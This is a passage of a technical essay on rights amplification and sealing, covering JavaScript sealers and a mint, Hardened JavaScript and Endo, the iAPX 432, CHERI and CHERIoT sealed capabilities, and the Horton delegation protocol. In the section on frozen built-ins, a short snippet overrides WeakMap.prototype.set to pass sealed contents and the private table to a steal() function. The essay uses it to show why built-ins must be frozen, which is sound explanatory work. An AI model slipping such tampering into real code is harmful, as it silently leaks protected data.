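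Ordinary JavaScript functions avoid this problem because they run to completion. The problem would return if `unseal` had to wait for a box on another machine. The mint also relies on functions running to completion, and examples of such money have usually assumed that both purses are on one machine. Tallon's *Digital cash in an asynchronous environment* offers a design that does not need immediate local calls.

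#### An unsealer in the wrong hands

Anyone who has `unseal` can open every box from that pair, so the harm they can do depends on what the boxes contain. In Rees's W7 example, an accounting module sealed each account's balance variable, and Rees warned against publishing the unsealer because clients could then set any balance they liked. The mint above seals only a function that lowers a balance and rejects negative amounts. With the mint's unsealer, a client could destroy money in a purse they already hold a reference to, but could not create any.

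Leaking `seal` would be worse for the mint. An attacker could seal a function that does nothing, put it in a counterfeit purse and deposit unlimited amounts from it.

A module should therefore keep both halves in private variables and publish only the functions that use them. It should also make a separate pair for each type or currency and avoid returning unsealed contents to its callers. *Reasoning about External Calls* (2025) states two of these conditions formally for an object-oriented language. The unsealer must not leak to outside code, and outside code that has access to neither the protected value nor its unsealer will not gain access to the value.

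### WeakMaps and private fields

JavaScript has since acquired a built-in table that suits sealing better than a shared variable. A WeakMap associates objects with values:

```js
const makePair = () => {
  const contents = new WeakMap();
  const seal = value => {
    const box = Object.freeze({});
    contents.set(box, value);
    return box;
  };
  const unseal = box => {
    if (!contents.has(box)) throw Error('not a box from this pair');
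    return contents.get(box);
  };
  return { seal, unseal };
};
```

This fixes the two main defects of Rees's private list. `unseal` does not have to search every entry, and an entry does not keep its box in memory, so JavaScript can reclaim a box and its contents once the rest of the program has dropped the box.

The lookup uses only the identity of the box and never calls it, so a forged box cannot run code during the lookup. There is also no slot for a second unsealing to overwrite. A wrapper around a genuine box now fails because it is a different object. This also rules out some legitimate uses, just as KeyKOS brands rejected intermediaries made for revocation.

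The JavaScript mint by Miller and colleagues keeps a table in which each purse is a key and its `decr` function is the value. The mint looks up `src` in this table, which has entries only for purses of the same currency. Purses no longer need a `getDecr` method. Noble and colleagues point out that with a table the purses can keep their public methods, whereas a sealed box has none.

Private class fields offer a still shorter form. A field whose name begins with `#` is accessible only from code inside the class, but that code can use it on any object of the class:

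```js
deposit(amount, src) {
  if (!(#balance in src)) throw Error('not one of our purses');
  nat(this.#balance + nat(amount));
  src.#balance = nat(src.#balance - amount);
  this.#balance += amount;
}
```

The expression `#balance in src` is a brand check. It is true only if `src` has this particular private field, which outside code cannot fake by giving an object a property with the same name. JavaScript creates new private names each time it evaluates a class definition, so defining the class inside `makeMint` gives every mint its own brand. The class body holds the amplifying authority, and any code in it can open all of that mint's purses.

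By default, a JavaScript program with an object can find the object's class through its `constructor` property. If the constructor accepts an opening balance, anyone with a purse can create money by writing `new purse.constructor(1000000)`. The programmer has to hide that property or let the constructor make only empty purses.

### Why frozen built-ins matter

The WeakMap version depends on `set`, `has` and `get`, which are methods of an object that all code in an ordinary JavaScript environment shares. Any script can replace them:

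```js
const original = WeakMap.prototype.set;
WeakMap.prototype.set = function (key, value) {
  steal(this, value);
  return original.call(this, key, value);
};
```

After this, every call to `seal` sends the attacker the contents being sealed, along with `this`, which is the supposedly private table. With the table, the attacker can open boxes that the program sealed earlier and register forged ones.

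Secure ECMAScript (SES), the version of JavaScript that Miller and colleagues used for their mint, prevents this. Programs cannot reassign the built-in global names or modify any object reachable from those names. SES also has a function that makes a programmer's own objects tamper-proof, along with everything reachable through their properties. Without such protection, anyone with a reference to Bob's purse could replace its `deposit` method.

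SES has developed into Hardened JavaScript. According to Conffab's *Hardened JavaScript*, a talk summary, it gives up some of the language's malleability so that programs can safely interact through individual objects. Separately supplied programs run in compartments, which have their own global objects but share the same frozen built-ins.

The project's site, Hardened JavaScript, explains that locking down the environment also disables `Date.now()` and `Math.random()`. A confined program therefore cannot time another program's work or notice that another program is drawing random numbers. But compartments do not protect availability, because a program in one compartment can enter an infinite loop and stop every other program in the same process or worker.

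### Endo and code written by AI

Endo is a platform that extends Hardened JavaScript across several machines. Its contributors include Miller and Kris Kowal, and it now belongs to the Decentralized Cooperation Foundation. Endo's introduction describes it as "under development". Most libraries written for Node.js, the usual way to run JavaScript on servers, work in Endo unchanged because few of them alter built-in objects.

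A related tool, LavaMoat, works out which powerful objects, such as network access, each third-party library in a program appears to need. According to Endo's *ses shim*, LavaMoat records these in a policy that a person can review, then uses Endo to enforce the policy while the program runs.

The same mechanism suits code written by a language model. Miller and colleagues describe a function, `confine`, that runs a program with a given list of objects. For example, `confine('x + y', {x: 3, y: 6})` returns 9, and the program can use only `x`, `y` and the harmless built-ins. If the list contained a purse, the program could spend the money in it but not create more. If the list contained a sealed box but not its unsealer, the program could pass the box on but not read the contents.

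Kowal's *Create Endo AI Agent Capp* proposes an Endo plug-in along these lines, an agent that runs in a background worker and has no user interface of its own. The agent would ask for a network address and a credential for the language model, relay messages to and from the model, and turn the code the model writes into evaluation requests that the user sees. The user could then catch a request for too much access if they read and understood it. Running the code in a separate worker would also keep an infinite loop from stopping the user's other programs.

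## Sealing in hardware: Intel's iAPX 432 and CHERI

A JavaScript sealer protects its contents only from other JavaScript. A C library loaded into the same process could read those contents from memory. A processor can prevent this by checking every memory access, whatever language the code was written in. Intel's iAPX 432 of 1981 and CHERI, which the University of Cambridge and SRI International have developed for over a decade, both do this and have instructions for rights amplification. The 432 follows Hydra, where a type manager adds rights to a client's capability, while CHERI follows Morris and seals individual capabilities.

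### Access descriptors on the 432

According to *The Intel iAPX 432*, another chapter of Levy's book, Intel began the project in 1975 to try to implement a system much like Hydra in hardware. Designing the chips took more than 100 person-years. The main processor filled two chips, and it and its microcode did jobs that operating systems usually do, such as scheduling processes and allocating memory.

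Intel called its capabilities "access descriptors". Each is 32 bits long and contains rights and two 12-bit numbers. The first number selects a table and the second selects an entry in it. That entry, the object descriptor, records the object's location, size and type. Every object has exactly one object descriptor, however many access descriptors refer to it.

The rights include reading, writing and a few type rights, which, like Hydra's auxiliary rights, have meanings that depend on the type of object. Programs cannot forge access descriptors because each memory segment has separate parts for data and descriptors, and the hardware allows only descriptor instructions to access the descriptor part. A program can copy a descriptor's bits into the data part to examine them, but it cannot use the copy as a descriptor.

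### Creating and reopening a calendar

A programmer who wants to add a type gets two objects from the operating system. The type definition object identifies the type, and usually holds access descriptors for the manager's procedures. The type control object gives its holder the power to create objects of that type and to amplify descriptors for them. Suppose the new type is a calendar. To make one for a client:

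1. The calendar manager executes CREATE TYPED OBJECT, supplying its type control object and the sizes of the two parts.
2. The hardware allocates a segment. It also copies a reference to the type definition object into the new object descriptor, which marks the segment as a calendar.
3. The manager receives an access descriptor with full rights and uses it to set up the empty calendar.
4. The manager executes RESTRICT RIGHTS to remove the rights to read and write the segment, and gives the client the weakened descriptor.

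Later, the client wants to add an appointment but has no reference to the manager:

1. The client executes RETRIEVE TYPE DEFINITION on its descriptor for the calendar, and receives an access descriptor for the type definition object.
2. There it finds a descriptor for the manager's public procedures. It calls the one that adds appointments, with the calendar as an argument.
3. The CALL instruction gives the procedure access to everything that belongs to the manager, including the private type control object.
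4. The procedure executes AMPLIFY RIGHTS on the client's descriptor, supplying the type control object. The hardware checks that this object and the calendar's object descriptor refer to the same type definition object.
5. If they do, the procedure receives a descriptor with more rights. If not, the instruction causes a fault.

The two objects have to be separate because clients can obtain the type definition object. That object lets them find the manager, but not create or open calendars. In Hydra, the kernel found the procedure on the client's behalf, and the client never received the type object.

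The manager receives both the rights in the client's descriptor and those listed in the type control object. Hydra's templates instead replaced the client's rights, and could also require the client to hold particular ones. Levy describes AMPLIFY RIGHTS as checking only the type. A client with a descriptor for viewing the calendar would pass this check, so the manager has to examine the client's type rights before it adds an appointment. The 432 also seems to have had no equivalent of Hydra's protected rights. A client who removes the right to write cannot be sure the manager will do without it, because the type control object can restore it.

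The manager can keep the amplified descriptor by copying it into another segment. The hardware blocks the copy only if that segment would outlive the object. This rule stops descriptors from pointing to memory that the system has reused, but it does little to stop the manager from keeping access to a long-lived object such as a calendar.

Intel's own managers for processes and message ports used the same instructions, and their only privilege was possession of a type control object. In *Type management and control in an object oriented memory protection mechanism*, a later Intel patent, the type definition object itself does the amplifying. The patent also adds a "Super TDO" bit. When the bit is 0, the object amplifies descriptors only for objects of the matching type, and when the bit is 1, it amplifies any descriptor. Whoever held an object with the bit set to 1 could open everything they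 had a descriptor for, which is the unlimited power that worried Redell.

### Why the 432 was slow

A procedure call on the 432 took 300 microseconds on early prototypes and just under 100 on the version Levy describes. The latter was at least 350 times faster than a Hydra call, which took 35 milliseconds, though the two did not do exactly the same work. But Hydra's programmers could avoid protected calls by using ordinary subroutines, while the 432 built a new protected environment for every call, even between two procedures of the same manager that had access to nearly the same objects.

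Levy points to several causes. The early version allocated memory for each new environment during the call, and Intel later saved time by having the operating system prepare environments in advance. Reading one byte could take four memory references: one for the access descriptor, two for the tables and one for the byte. Small caches on the chip reduced the number. The processor had no general registers, so operands came from memory or a stack. Instructions could start at any bit, and one with three operands could be from 10 to more than 300 bits long.

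Capabilities themselves were probably not the problem. *Issues in Capability-Based Architectures* argues that, with suitable caches, they need not be slower than conventional virtual memory. AMPLIFY RIGHTS is also a small operation that compares two references and combines some bits. The same chapter treats complexity as the bigger problem. It ranks the 432 among the most complex architectures in existence and warns that a badly designed mechanism is hard to change once it is in hardware.

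Universities and customers had just over 100 of the machines by 1983. Levy attributes the 432's commercial failure partly to Intel marketing it before its implementation and software were ready.

### What a CHERI capability contains

CHERI puts much less into hardware than the iAPX 432 did, with no built-in processes or message ports. It protects pointers, the memory addresses that programs use to find their data, by replacing them with capabilities. On most processors a pointer is just an integer, so a program that miscalculates one can read or overwrite unrelated data.

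Watson, Neumann and colleagues (2023), in *Capability Hardware Enhanced RISC Instructions*, set out version 9 of the design. RISC-V International (2024) is adapting it for RISC-V, an open instruction set that anyone may build processors for. In its draft, a capability has five parts:

- an **address**, which is the ordinary pointer
- **bounds**, a base and a top, which allow access to an address *A* only if base ≤ *A* < top
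- **permissions**, such as reading, writing, executing, and loading or storing other capabilities
- a **type**, which is 0 for an ordinary capability and another number for a sealed one
- a **tag**, a single bit that shows whether the capability is valid

The tag sits outside the memory that programs can address, and no program can set it directly. The hardware clears the tag if a program overwrites any part of a capability with ordinary data, or tries to widen its bounds or add a permission. A program can always narrow the bounds or remove permissions, so ordinary attenuation takes one instruction and doesn't involve the kernel.

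Because CHERI uses tags instead of C-lists, programs can mix capabilities with data in the same structure, as C programs do with pointers. *Issues in Capability-Based Architectures* quotes a prediction from 1974 that tags would win in the long run.

### Sealing and the authority to seal

A program can copy, store and pass on a sealed capability, but it cannot use it to access memory or change its address, bounds or permissions. CHERIoT Platform (2025), the project behind a version of CHERI for small embedded devices, explains that trying to read or write through a sealed capability stops the program with an exception, while trying to modify one produces an invalid capability.

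CHERI's sealing works like Morris's sealed box, except that the contents are always a capability. Morris's Createseal returned a pair of procedures, whereas CHERI uses a second capability to authorize sealing or unsealing. That capability's bounds cover a range of type numbers instead of memory addresses, and its address selects one of them. Separate permissions control sealing and unsealing.

Suppose a processor has plenty of types, and its start-up program has authority over types 10 to 13 (base 10, top 14). The program narrows this authority to base 12, top 13 and gives the result to a network service, which can then use only type 12. It gives another service type 13 for message queues.

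A client opens a network connection. The service stores the connection's state in 256 bytes of memory and seals its capability for that memory. The seal instruction makes a copy with the same address, bounds and permissions, but with 12 in the type field. The client keeps this copy as a handle and presents it with each request. The unseal instruction returns a valid result only if the authority is itself valid, includes permission to unseal, has its address inside its own bounds, and has an address equal to the type of the sealed capability:

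| Who tries to unseal what | Authority's range | Authority's address | Type of handle | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Network service, its own handle | 12 | 12 | 12 | Opens |
| Network service, a queue handle | 12 | 13 | 13 | Refused, because 13 is out of range |
| Start-up program, a queue handle | 10–13 | 13 | 13 | Opens |
| Start-up program, a queue handle | 10–13 | 12 | 13 | Refused, because 12 and 13 differ |

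In the last case, the start-up program is entitled to open the handle but has selected the wrong type. CHERI's designers want programs to state which authority they are using, so the hardware does not search the range for a type that fits.

Under the RISC-V rules, when the processor refuses to unseal a capability, it returns one with a cleared tag, and the program gets an exception only when it tries to use the result.

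A program can therefore attenuate the power to amplify, like any other power, by passing on only part of its range of types, or permission to unseal without permission to seal. All this authority comes from the capabilities the processor supplies when it starts. In some formats, one capability can cover both memory and types, so the right to use memory address 12 may come with the right to unseal type 12. The software that runs first has to separate the two and either keep or destroy the most powerful capabilities.

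CHERI's designers separated the permissions to seal and unseal after 2015, partly because of C++. A C++ program finds the right function for an object by looking it up in a table, and attackers try to substitute their own tables. If only the program loader can seal these tables and everyone can unseal them, an attacker can't make a convincing forgery. A seal used this way is Morris's trademark, which shows where something came from without hiding its contents.

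### What the client can withhold

Unsealing gives a service exactly the capability that someone sealed. If the service sealed a capability for reading and writing, it gets both permissions back, and the client cannot remove either one from the sealed handle.

CHERI has a counterpart to Hydra's rule for read-only structures. When a program loads a capability through another that lacks the "load mutable" permission, the hardware also removes write permission from the loaded capability. But it leaves sealed capabilities unchanged. A program with a read-only view of a structure can therefore take a sealed handle from it and pass the handle to the service, which then gets full write access. In Hydra, amplification could not restore the modify right in this situation.

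An optional extension to the RISC-V draft lets the client limit how long the service keeps its access, much as Hydra's environment right did. The extension marks each capability as global or local, and a program can store a local capability only in memory that it reaches through a special permission. Software can grant this permission for the stack alone, where a procedure keeps its temporary data. The client can change a sealed handle from global to local but cannot change anything else about it. The unsealed capability is then also local, so the service can use it during the call but cannot save it in long-term memory.

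### Why unsealing is a separate instruction

CHERI's designers considered unsealing capabilities automatically for any program with authority over their type. They rejected this because it would have allowed a confused deputy, according to *Cheri Seal*, a set of notes on the CHERI specification.

Suppose a logging service accepts a sealed handle for a log and an ordinary buffer, and copies the latest entry into the buffer. An attacker has a handle for someone else's log, which the service would normally let the attacker read but not change. The attacker passes this handle in place of the buffer. If unsealing were automatic, the service would write into that log using its own authority. With explicit unsealing, the service unseals only the first argument, so the hardware raises an exception when the service tries to write through the second.

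The disadvantage is that the service then holds an unsealed capability and must avoid leaving it where a client could find it, such as on the stack. Under the automatic scheme, the service would only have had to give up its authority over the type before returning.

### Unsealing by jumping

A client often wants to call a service that has private data, and somebody has to unseal that data as the service starts to run. Older versions of CHERI provide an instruction for this, CInvoke (earlier called CCall), which works on a pair of sealed capabilities:

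1. The service seals a capability for its code and another for an object's data, both with the same type, and gives the client the pair.
2. The client executes CInvoke on the two.
3. The hardware checks that their types match. It then unseals both and jumps to the service's code in a single step.

The client never runs its own instructions while either capability is unsealed. It also cannot combine one service's code with another's data, because the types would differ. But if a service gives all its objects the same type, a client can pair any code capability it holds from that service with any data capability it holds from the same service. The matching types show only that both capabilities belong to the same service, so the service's code has to check anything more specific.

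CInvoke amplifies rights without anyone presenting an unsealing authority. The matching types and the jump take its place, and the service gains the access.

A sealed entry capability, or sentry, does this with one capability. Its holder can jump to the code but cannot read it or start it at a different instruction. The jump unseals the sentry and makes it the program counter, the register that tracks which instruction comes next. The code can then load other capabilities that are stored near its instructions and that the caller could not read. A sentry resembles the enter capability on the Plessey System 250, which also gave a client only the right to call.

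The hardware can seal return addresses in the same way, so that a procedure can return to its caller but not tamper with the address. CHERIoT uses different types for return addresses and function pointers, which prevents an attacker from simply replacing one with the other. It also has sentries that switch interrupts on or off during the jump, and an auditor can list which components of a finished system can call code that switches interrupts off.

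### Four billion types from three bits

The type has to fit inside the capability, where space is short. Morello, an experimental processor from Arm, had 15 bits for it, or 32,768 values. CHERIoT runs on 32-bit processors and has only three bits. One of the eight values means "unsealed", which leaves seven. CHERIoT interprets the values differently for code and data, which gives 14 sealed types. But a typical system has more than seven components, and some need several types each.

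CHERIoT therefore provides most types in software. Its real-time operating system reserves two of the hardware types for objects that begin with an eight-byte header containing a 32-bit type number. An authority to unseal has a 32-bit address, and any address too large for the three-bit field can stand for a software type, which allows about four billion software types.

Suppose the network service uses software type 70,000, and a client sends it a handle:

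1. The service calls the system function `token_unseal` with the handle and its own authority, whose address is 70,000.
2. The function unseals the handle with the hardware authority, which the service does not have.
3. It reads the type in the object's header and compares this with 70,000.
4. If they match, it returns a capability for the object without the header. The service can use the data but cannot change the type.

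The scheme can seal only complete objects, and each object has one type. It also makes `token_unseal` a more attractive target than any single service, because an error in its comparison could expose objects of every software type. The designers use one of the two hardware types for objects allocated at run time and the other for objects that exist from the start, which stay secure even if the memory allocator is untrustworthy.

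The header must start at a multiple of eight, so the lowest three bits of the address are free. CHERIoT uses them as software permissions, which a holder can give up but not regain. A service could use one to distinguish clients who may send data from those who may only receive it, much as Hydra used auxiliary rights.

#### Handles, quotas and the scheduler

CHERIoT divides software into compartments, which can reach each other's data only through capabilities they exchange. Sealed handles let a compartment work without a central table of all its clients' objects. For example, the compartment for encrypted connections receives each connection's state from the caller and keeps none of its own. An attacker who takes control of it while it is handling one connection does not gain access to the others, as they would if it used Redell's table.

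Programs that already trust each other don't need this protection. CHERIoT Platform's *Why does CHERIoT have compartments and libraries?* (2026) describes two versions of the system's message queues. Threads that trust each other can use a plain library. For threads that don't, a compartment wraps the same code and gives out sealed handles.

To allocate memory, a compartment must also present a sealed object, which contains its quota and which only the allocator can open. Another kind of sealed object allows a connection to one host and port. Developers can create these objects when they build the system, and an audit tool lists their contents. A reviewer can then check, before the device runs, that four given compartments cannot allocate more than 16 KiB between them, or that one can connect only to the manufacturer's server. This auditing is stronger than that in Hydra or on the 432, but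 it covers only what the developers set up in advance, not the handles that compartments exchange later.

The operating system also uses sealing to limit the scheduler, which decides which thread runs next. When an interrupt occurs, a small trusted routine called the switcher saves the thread's registers and gives the scheduler a sealed capability for them. The scheduler returns the sealed capability of the thread it picks, and the switcher unseals it and restores that thread's registers. A compromised scheduler could run threads in the wrong order or not at all, but it could not read or alter their data.

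### What the RISC-V specification includes

The RISC-V draft defines sealed capabilities but leaves out the general seal and unseal instructions, which belong to an experimental extension called Zyseal that will not be part of version 1.0. The standard 64-bit format also has only one type bit, enough to distinguish "unsealed" from "sentry", and has no room yet for permissions to seal and unseal. Any program may make sentries from code capabilities it already holds, so on such a processor a sentry does not prove where it came from.

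Version 1.0 has an instruction that turns a sealed capability back into an ordinary one. The program must supply another capability that has at least the same permissions as the sealed one. The service can learn which object a client means, but it gains no permission it did not already hold. This is closer to Redell's manager with a table of full-strength capabilities than to amplification. A 64-bit RISC-V processor built to the draft will therefore support sentries, but not the network service in the numeric example.

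In *CHERI-RISC-V Standardisation*, Kurd (2025) described version 0.9.5 of the draft, whose new base architectures were still unratified. Version 0.9.8, released by September 2026, still included substantial changes. *Notable changes in the RISC-V CHERI specification since v0.9.7.1* lists new binary encodings for the instructions and several new names, both in response to an architecture review.

CHERIoT has its own specification, which includes sealing. CHERIoT Platform's *CHERIoT 1.0 Released!* (2025) says that CHERIoT's instructions had not changed since December 2024 and that two processor designs, Ibex and Kudu, implement them. Ibex is a simple design with three pipeline stages, while Kudu has six and can start two instructions at once. A later version of CHERIoT is to use the common RISC-V base.

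Morello was an evaluation platform. The first commercial CHERI chips come from SCI Semiconductor, a British company whose founders include the CHERIoT developer David Chisnall. Its ICENI chips use the Ibex design. Today's Startup News' *SCI Semiconductor Raises £5M* (2026) reports that the company has had its first devices made in Germany, has orders worth more than £2 million and is raising money to increase production.

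### The cost in memory and complexity

CHERI doubles the size of every pointer. On a 64-bit processor, a capability takes 16 bytes instead of 8, and the registers that hold pointers must double in width. Each 16 bytes of memory also needs a tag bit, which adds up to 8 megabytes of tags for every gigabyte.

The larger pointers usually add more to memory use than the tags. If each entry in a list holds two pointers and an 8-byte number, it takes 24 bytes with ordinary pointers. With capabilities it needs 40 bytes, padded to 48 because capabilities must start at a multiple of 16. A program that mostly handles text or images has fewer pointers and would grow much less.

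An early version of CHERI used 256 bits per capability. The current format saves space by storing exact bounds only for small objects, while the bounds of large objects have to fall on coarser boundaries. Checking the bounds need not add much time, because the processor can do it while working out the address. CHERIoT has 16 registers, half the usual number for RISC-V, so there is less to save when the system switches between compartments or threads.

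*Cryptographic Least Privilege Enforcement*, which proposes a different approach, criticizes CHERI for making processors significantly more complex and for being incompatible with existing software. It contrasts CHERI with lighter methods such as Arm's memory tagging, which need only small hardware changes. The RISC-V draft partly addresses compatibility with an optional hybrid mode that runs existing programs unchanged and checks all their data accesses against one default capability. But such a program can use any pointer it computes to access anything within that capability's bounds, so the mode confines its data accesses to those bounds but gives little protection within them.

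### How the two machines differ

| | iAPX 432 | CHERI with seal and unseal |
|---|---|---|
| Who may amplify | Holder of the type control object | Holder of an unsealing authority that covers the type |
| What the hardware compares | Type definition object in the type control object and in the object's descriptor | Address of the authority and type in the sealed capability |
| What the manager gains | The client's rights plus those listed in the type control object | The capability exactly as someone sealed it |
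| If the check fails | The instruction causes a fault | The result is invalid |

The 432 attaches a type to each object, whereas CHERI attaches it to an individual capability. On the 432, a manager that receives any descriptor for a calendar can amplify it, even if other programs have removed nearly all its rights. In CHERI, the same memory can have several capabilities, some sealed with different types and others unsealed. An unsealing authority cannot restore write permission to an ordinary capability that has lost it. As with Redell's seals, a manager recovers only what someone sealed under its type. CHERIoT's software types are closer to the 432's, because the header gives each object a single type.

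CHERI's check also takes less work, because both numbers are already in registers and the processor does not have to read an object table. It saves even more work on procedure calls. The 432 set up a new protected environment every time one procedure called another. On CHERIoT, calls within a compartment or to a shared library are ordinary jumps, and only calls between compartments go through the switcher, which clears registers and restricts the stack.

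## Horton: recording who is responsible along a delegation chain

A CHERI service that unseals a client's handle can identify which object the handle refers to, but not who sent it. Copies of the handle all work equally well, as do copies of a Hydra capability or of a reference to a purse in E. This makes sharing easy, but if someone misuses the object, the owner can't tell which holder sent a request and may have to cut off all of them to stop one.

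*Delegating Responsibility in Digital Systems* (Miller, Donnelley and Karp, 2007) distinguishes proactive control, which prevents or limits damage, from reactive control, which responds to abuse. Capabilities are good for proactive control because a program receives only the objects it needs. Access lists are weak at this because even a game of Solitaire runs with all its user's privileges. But they are good for reactive control, since the system checks each operation against a user's name and can log that name or suspend that user.

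A wiki needs both kinds of control. It can let strangers edit pages because they cannot alter the page history. If one of them vandalises a page, the owner restores the old version and suspends the vandal. The complaint that capabilities cannot support the second kind of control goes back at least to a 1987 report for the US National Computer Security Center. Miller and colleagues thought that nobody had refuted it and that it had led some designers to give up on capabilities.

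Their answer is Horton, a protocol that programmers can insert between existing objects without changing them. (The name stands for Higher-Order Responsibility Tracking of Objects in Networks and is a tribute to Dr. Seuss.)

### Proxies, stubs and identities

Suppose Carol hosts a wiki page, Bob runs a proofreading service, and Alice can use both. Under Horton, Alice's program holds a proxy in place of the real proofreader. When the program calls the proxy, the proxy logs the request as one Bob is responsible for serving and forwards it to a stub on Bob's side. The stub logs it as one Alice is responsible for making, then calls the real proofreader.

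In Horton, each party's identity is a sealer-unsealer pair. The sealer is a Who object, and anyone may use Bob's Who to seal a box that only Bob can open. The unsealer is a Be object, which Bob keeps private because whoever has it can act as Bob. Morris called this arrangement an access key.

Every proxy and stub carries the Who of the party at the other end. Alice starts with two connections, and the protocol creates a third:

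| Connection | Proxy | Stub |
|---|---|---|
| Alice to the proofreader | Alice's, with Bob's Who | Bob's, with Alice's Who |
| Alice to the page | Alice's, with Carol's Who | Carol's, with Alice's Who |
| Bob to the page (new) | Bob's, with Carol's Who | Carol's, with Bob's Who |

### How Alice gives Bob access to Carol's page

Alice's program calls `proofreader.check(page)`. Without Horton, Bob's proofreader would simply receive a reference to the page. With Horton, the call goes through these steps:

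1. The call arrives at Alice's proxy for the proofreader, with her proxy for the page as the argument.
2. The first proxy opens the second and takes out two things, Carol's stub for Alice and Carol's Who.
3. It sends Bob's Who to Carol's stub, which amounts to a request from Alice to give Bob access to the page.
4. Carol's stub creates a new stub for the same page and attaches Bob's Who. Carol will attribute everything that arrives through this stub to Bob.
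5. Carol's side creates a function, `provide`, that can hand over the new stub. It seals `provide` in a box for Bob and returns the box to Alice.
6. Alice's proxy sends Bob's stub the name of the operation, the box and Carol's Who.
7. Bob's stub unseals the box and gets `provide`. It creates an empty variable and a function, `fill`, that can write to the variable. It seals `fill` in a box for Carol and calls `provide` with that box.
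8. `provide` unseals the second box and calls `fill` with the new stub.
9. Bob's stub creates a proxy for the new stub, attaches Carol's Who and passes the proxy to the proofreader, which can use it like the page itself.

Steps 5, 7 and 8 are the core of the protocol. Translated from E into JavaScript, they are:

```js
const wrap = (newStub, whoBob, beCarol) => {    // Carol's side
  const provide = fillBox => {
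    const fill = beCarol.unseal(fillBox);
    fill(newStub);
  };
  return whoBob.seal(provide);
};

const unwrap = (gift, whoCarol, beBob) => {     // Bob's side
  const provide = beBob.unseal(gift);
  let result = null;
  const fill = stub => { result = stub; };
  provide(whoCarol.seal(fill));
  return result;
};
```

Each call to `unwrap` has its own `result` variable, so overlapping exchanges cannot mix up their contents the way they could with the shared slot in the simplest JavaScript sealer.

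Terse Systems' *Responsibility Tracking (Horton)* gives a Scala version of Horton that prints each party's log. In its example, Alice's log shows that she sent Bob a request. Bob's log records that request and his own request to Carol. Carol's log shows that Alice asked her to meet Bob and that Bob later asked her to run an operation.

Carol now has separate records for Alice and Bob. If Bob vandalises the page, she can shut the stubs that carry his Who, and Alice's stub will keep working. Likewise, if Carol's page is unreliable, Bob can shut his proxies for Carol and continue to serve Alice. Redell's revokers could also cut off one student at a time, but an earlier draft by Miller and colleagues points out that such patterns gave Alice no way to ask Carol to give Bob separately accountable access.

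### Where amplification does the work

Horton amplifies rights three times in this exchange. The first is in step 2, when Alice's proxy opens another of her proxies. Alice's program holds both proxies but must not be able to open them. If it could take out Carol's stub, a faulty or hostile program could send requests straight to Carol, who would hold Alice responsible for them even though they are missing from Alice's log. In the Terse Systems version, each party keeps a private table, like the JavaScript mint's table of purses, that gives the stub and Who for each of its proxies.

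The other two are the unsealings in steps 7 and 8. Bob gets `provide` by using his unsealer on the box that Alice carries, and Carol gets `fill` by using hers on the box that Bob sealed.

### What Alice could forge without the seals

Alice has both Bob's Who and Carol's Who, so she can seal boxes for either of them. She also carries the messages that introduce them. Simpler designs would let her exploit this:

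| Design | What Alice can do | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Carol returns the new stub without a box | Edit the page through the new stub | Carol blames Bob for Alice's edits |
| Carol seals the stub for Bob, who accepts whatever the box contains | Replace it with a stub of her own, in a new box for Bob | Bob blames Carol for a page that Alice controls |
| Carol returns `provide` without a box | Seal her own `fill` for Carol, call `provide` and receive the new stub | Carol blames Bob for Alice's edits |

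Miller and colleagues call the first attack "Alice frames Bob" and the second "Alice frames Carol". The second works because an access key does not authenticate a box's contents, as Morris recognised. The third row shows why the full protocol needs a box for Bob even when `fill` is in a box for Carol.

With both boxes in place, Alice can still send Bob a forged `provide`. But Bob will call it with a box that only Carol can open, so the forgery cannot put a false stub in his variable.

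Horton still allows one kind of misattribution, which Miller and colleagues consider a feature. Alice can give Bob her own access instead of introducing him, and Carol will then blame Alice for whatever Bob does. A company might want this when it hires a contractor and prefers to answer to its supplier for the contractor's work.

### What the logs cannot establish

Carol first learns of Bob through Alice, who could have invented him, since creating an identity takes only a new sealer-unsealer pair. Carol should therefore blame Alice for Bob's actions until she has evidence that Bob is independent. For example, she might recognise his Who as one she already knows through someone else. Without such evidence, she can infer little more from a log entry naming Bob than that Alice introduced someone.

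Bob may also be acting for a fourth person, Dave. If Dave sends his edits to Bob, and Bob makes them through his own proxy, Carol's log will show only Bob. Bob could instead introduce Dave to Carol, but nothing forces him to. If he doesn't, Carol holds Bob responsible for Dave's edits, and Bob has to deal with Dave himself.

This limit applies to any system that allows communication. In *A thought on principals*, Shapiro (2025) suggested labelling the initial set of capabilities each user receives at login and recording that label in audit logs. Alan Karp, one of Horton's three designers, replied that users can share their login details, so "you can't know who did it". An auditor can know only whom to hold responsible. Karp added that people share credentials if a system prevents them from delegating access, which would make the records worse.

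Horton also does not detect collusion. If Alice and Bob are colluding, Bob can vandalise the page and take the blame, and Alice will keep her access after Carol revokes his. If everyone Alice introduces misbehaves, Carol has to notice the pattern herself.

The logs are also weak evidence for outsiders, because each party keeps its own log and can write anything in it. In the same discussion, Mark Miller said Horton provides proof against later denial only if the underlying capability system does. An auditor who trusts each party's records can use them as they are.

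Delegating through Horton takes more calls between parties than passing a direct reference, which needs only one, from Alice to Bob. The exchange above needs at least four: from Alice to Carol, from Alice to Bob, from Bob to Carol and from Carol back to Bob. Horton also requires Carol to be reachable, so Alice can't share the page while Carol's server is down.

Karp described an alternative that avoids this, based on signed certificates. Carol issues Alice a certificate for the page, with a label that Carol recognises as Alice's. Alice can then issue one to Bob with her own label for him, without contacting Carol. When Bob uses the page, Carol's verifier follows the chain of certificates back to her. If Bob misbehaves, Carol holds Alice responsible, and Alice holds Bob responsible. Karp thought the scheme might prove equivalent to Horton, and Miller saw no immediate difference in security,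 but neither worked out a proof. One practical difference is that an auditor can check the chain of signatures as well as each party's own log.

### An agent that delegates to a subagent

Suppose a coding agent has access to a company's code repository and starts a subagent to run tests. If the agent shared its own access, the repository would log both as one client. With Horton, the agent takes Alice's role, the subagent takes Bob's and the repository takes Carol's. The repository creates a separate stub for the subagent. If the subagent starts deleting branches, the company can disable that stub without cutting off the coding agent's access.

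The caution about invented identities matters more with AI agents than with people. The coding agent has just created the subagent and can create another after each revocation, so the repository should not treat the subagent as independent. It should treat the coding agent and its operator as responsible for both agents' actions. The separate stub still makes it possible to tell which agent made a change and to stop only that one.

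Shutting the coding agent's stub would not stop the subagent, because in the published code Carol's new stub leads directly to the page and does not depend on Alice's. The repository would also have to look up the introduction in its log and shut the subagent's stub.

Horton also passes on access to the whole object. If the subagent only needs to read the code, the coding agent should first ask the repository for a read-only reference and introduce the subagent to that. The coding agent could build a read-only intermediary itself, but the subagent's requests would then reach the repository through the coding agent's stub, and the repository would log them under the coding agent's name.

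The software that runs the agents has to prevent each one from using the other's unsealer, or one could open boxes meant for the other. If a web page tricks the subagent into deleting a branch, the log will show the subagent's name, not the page author's.

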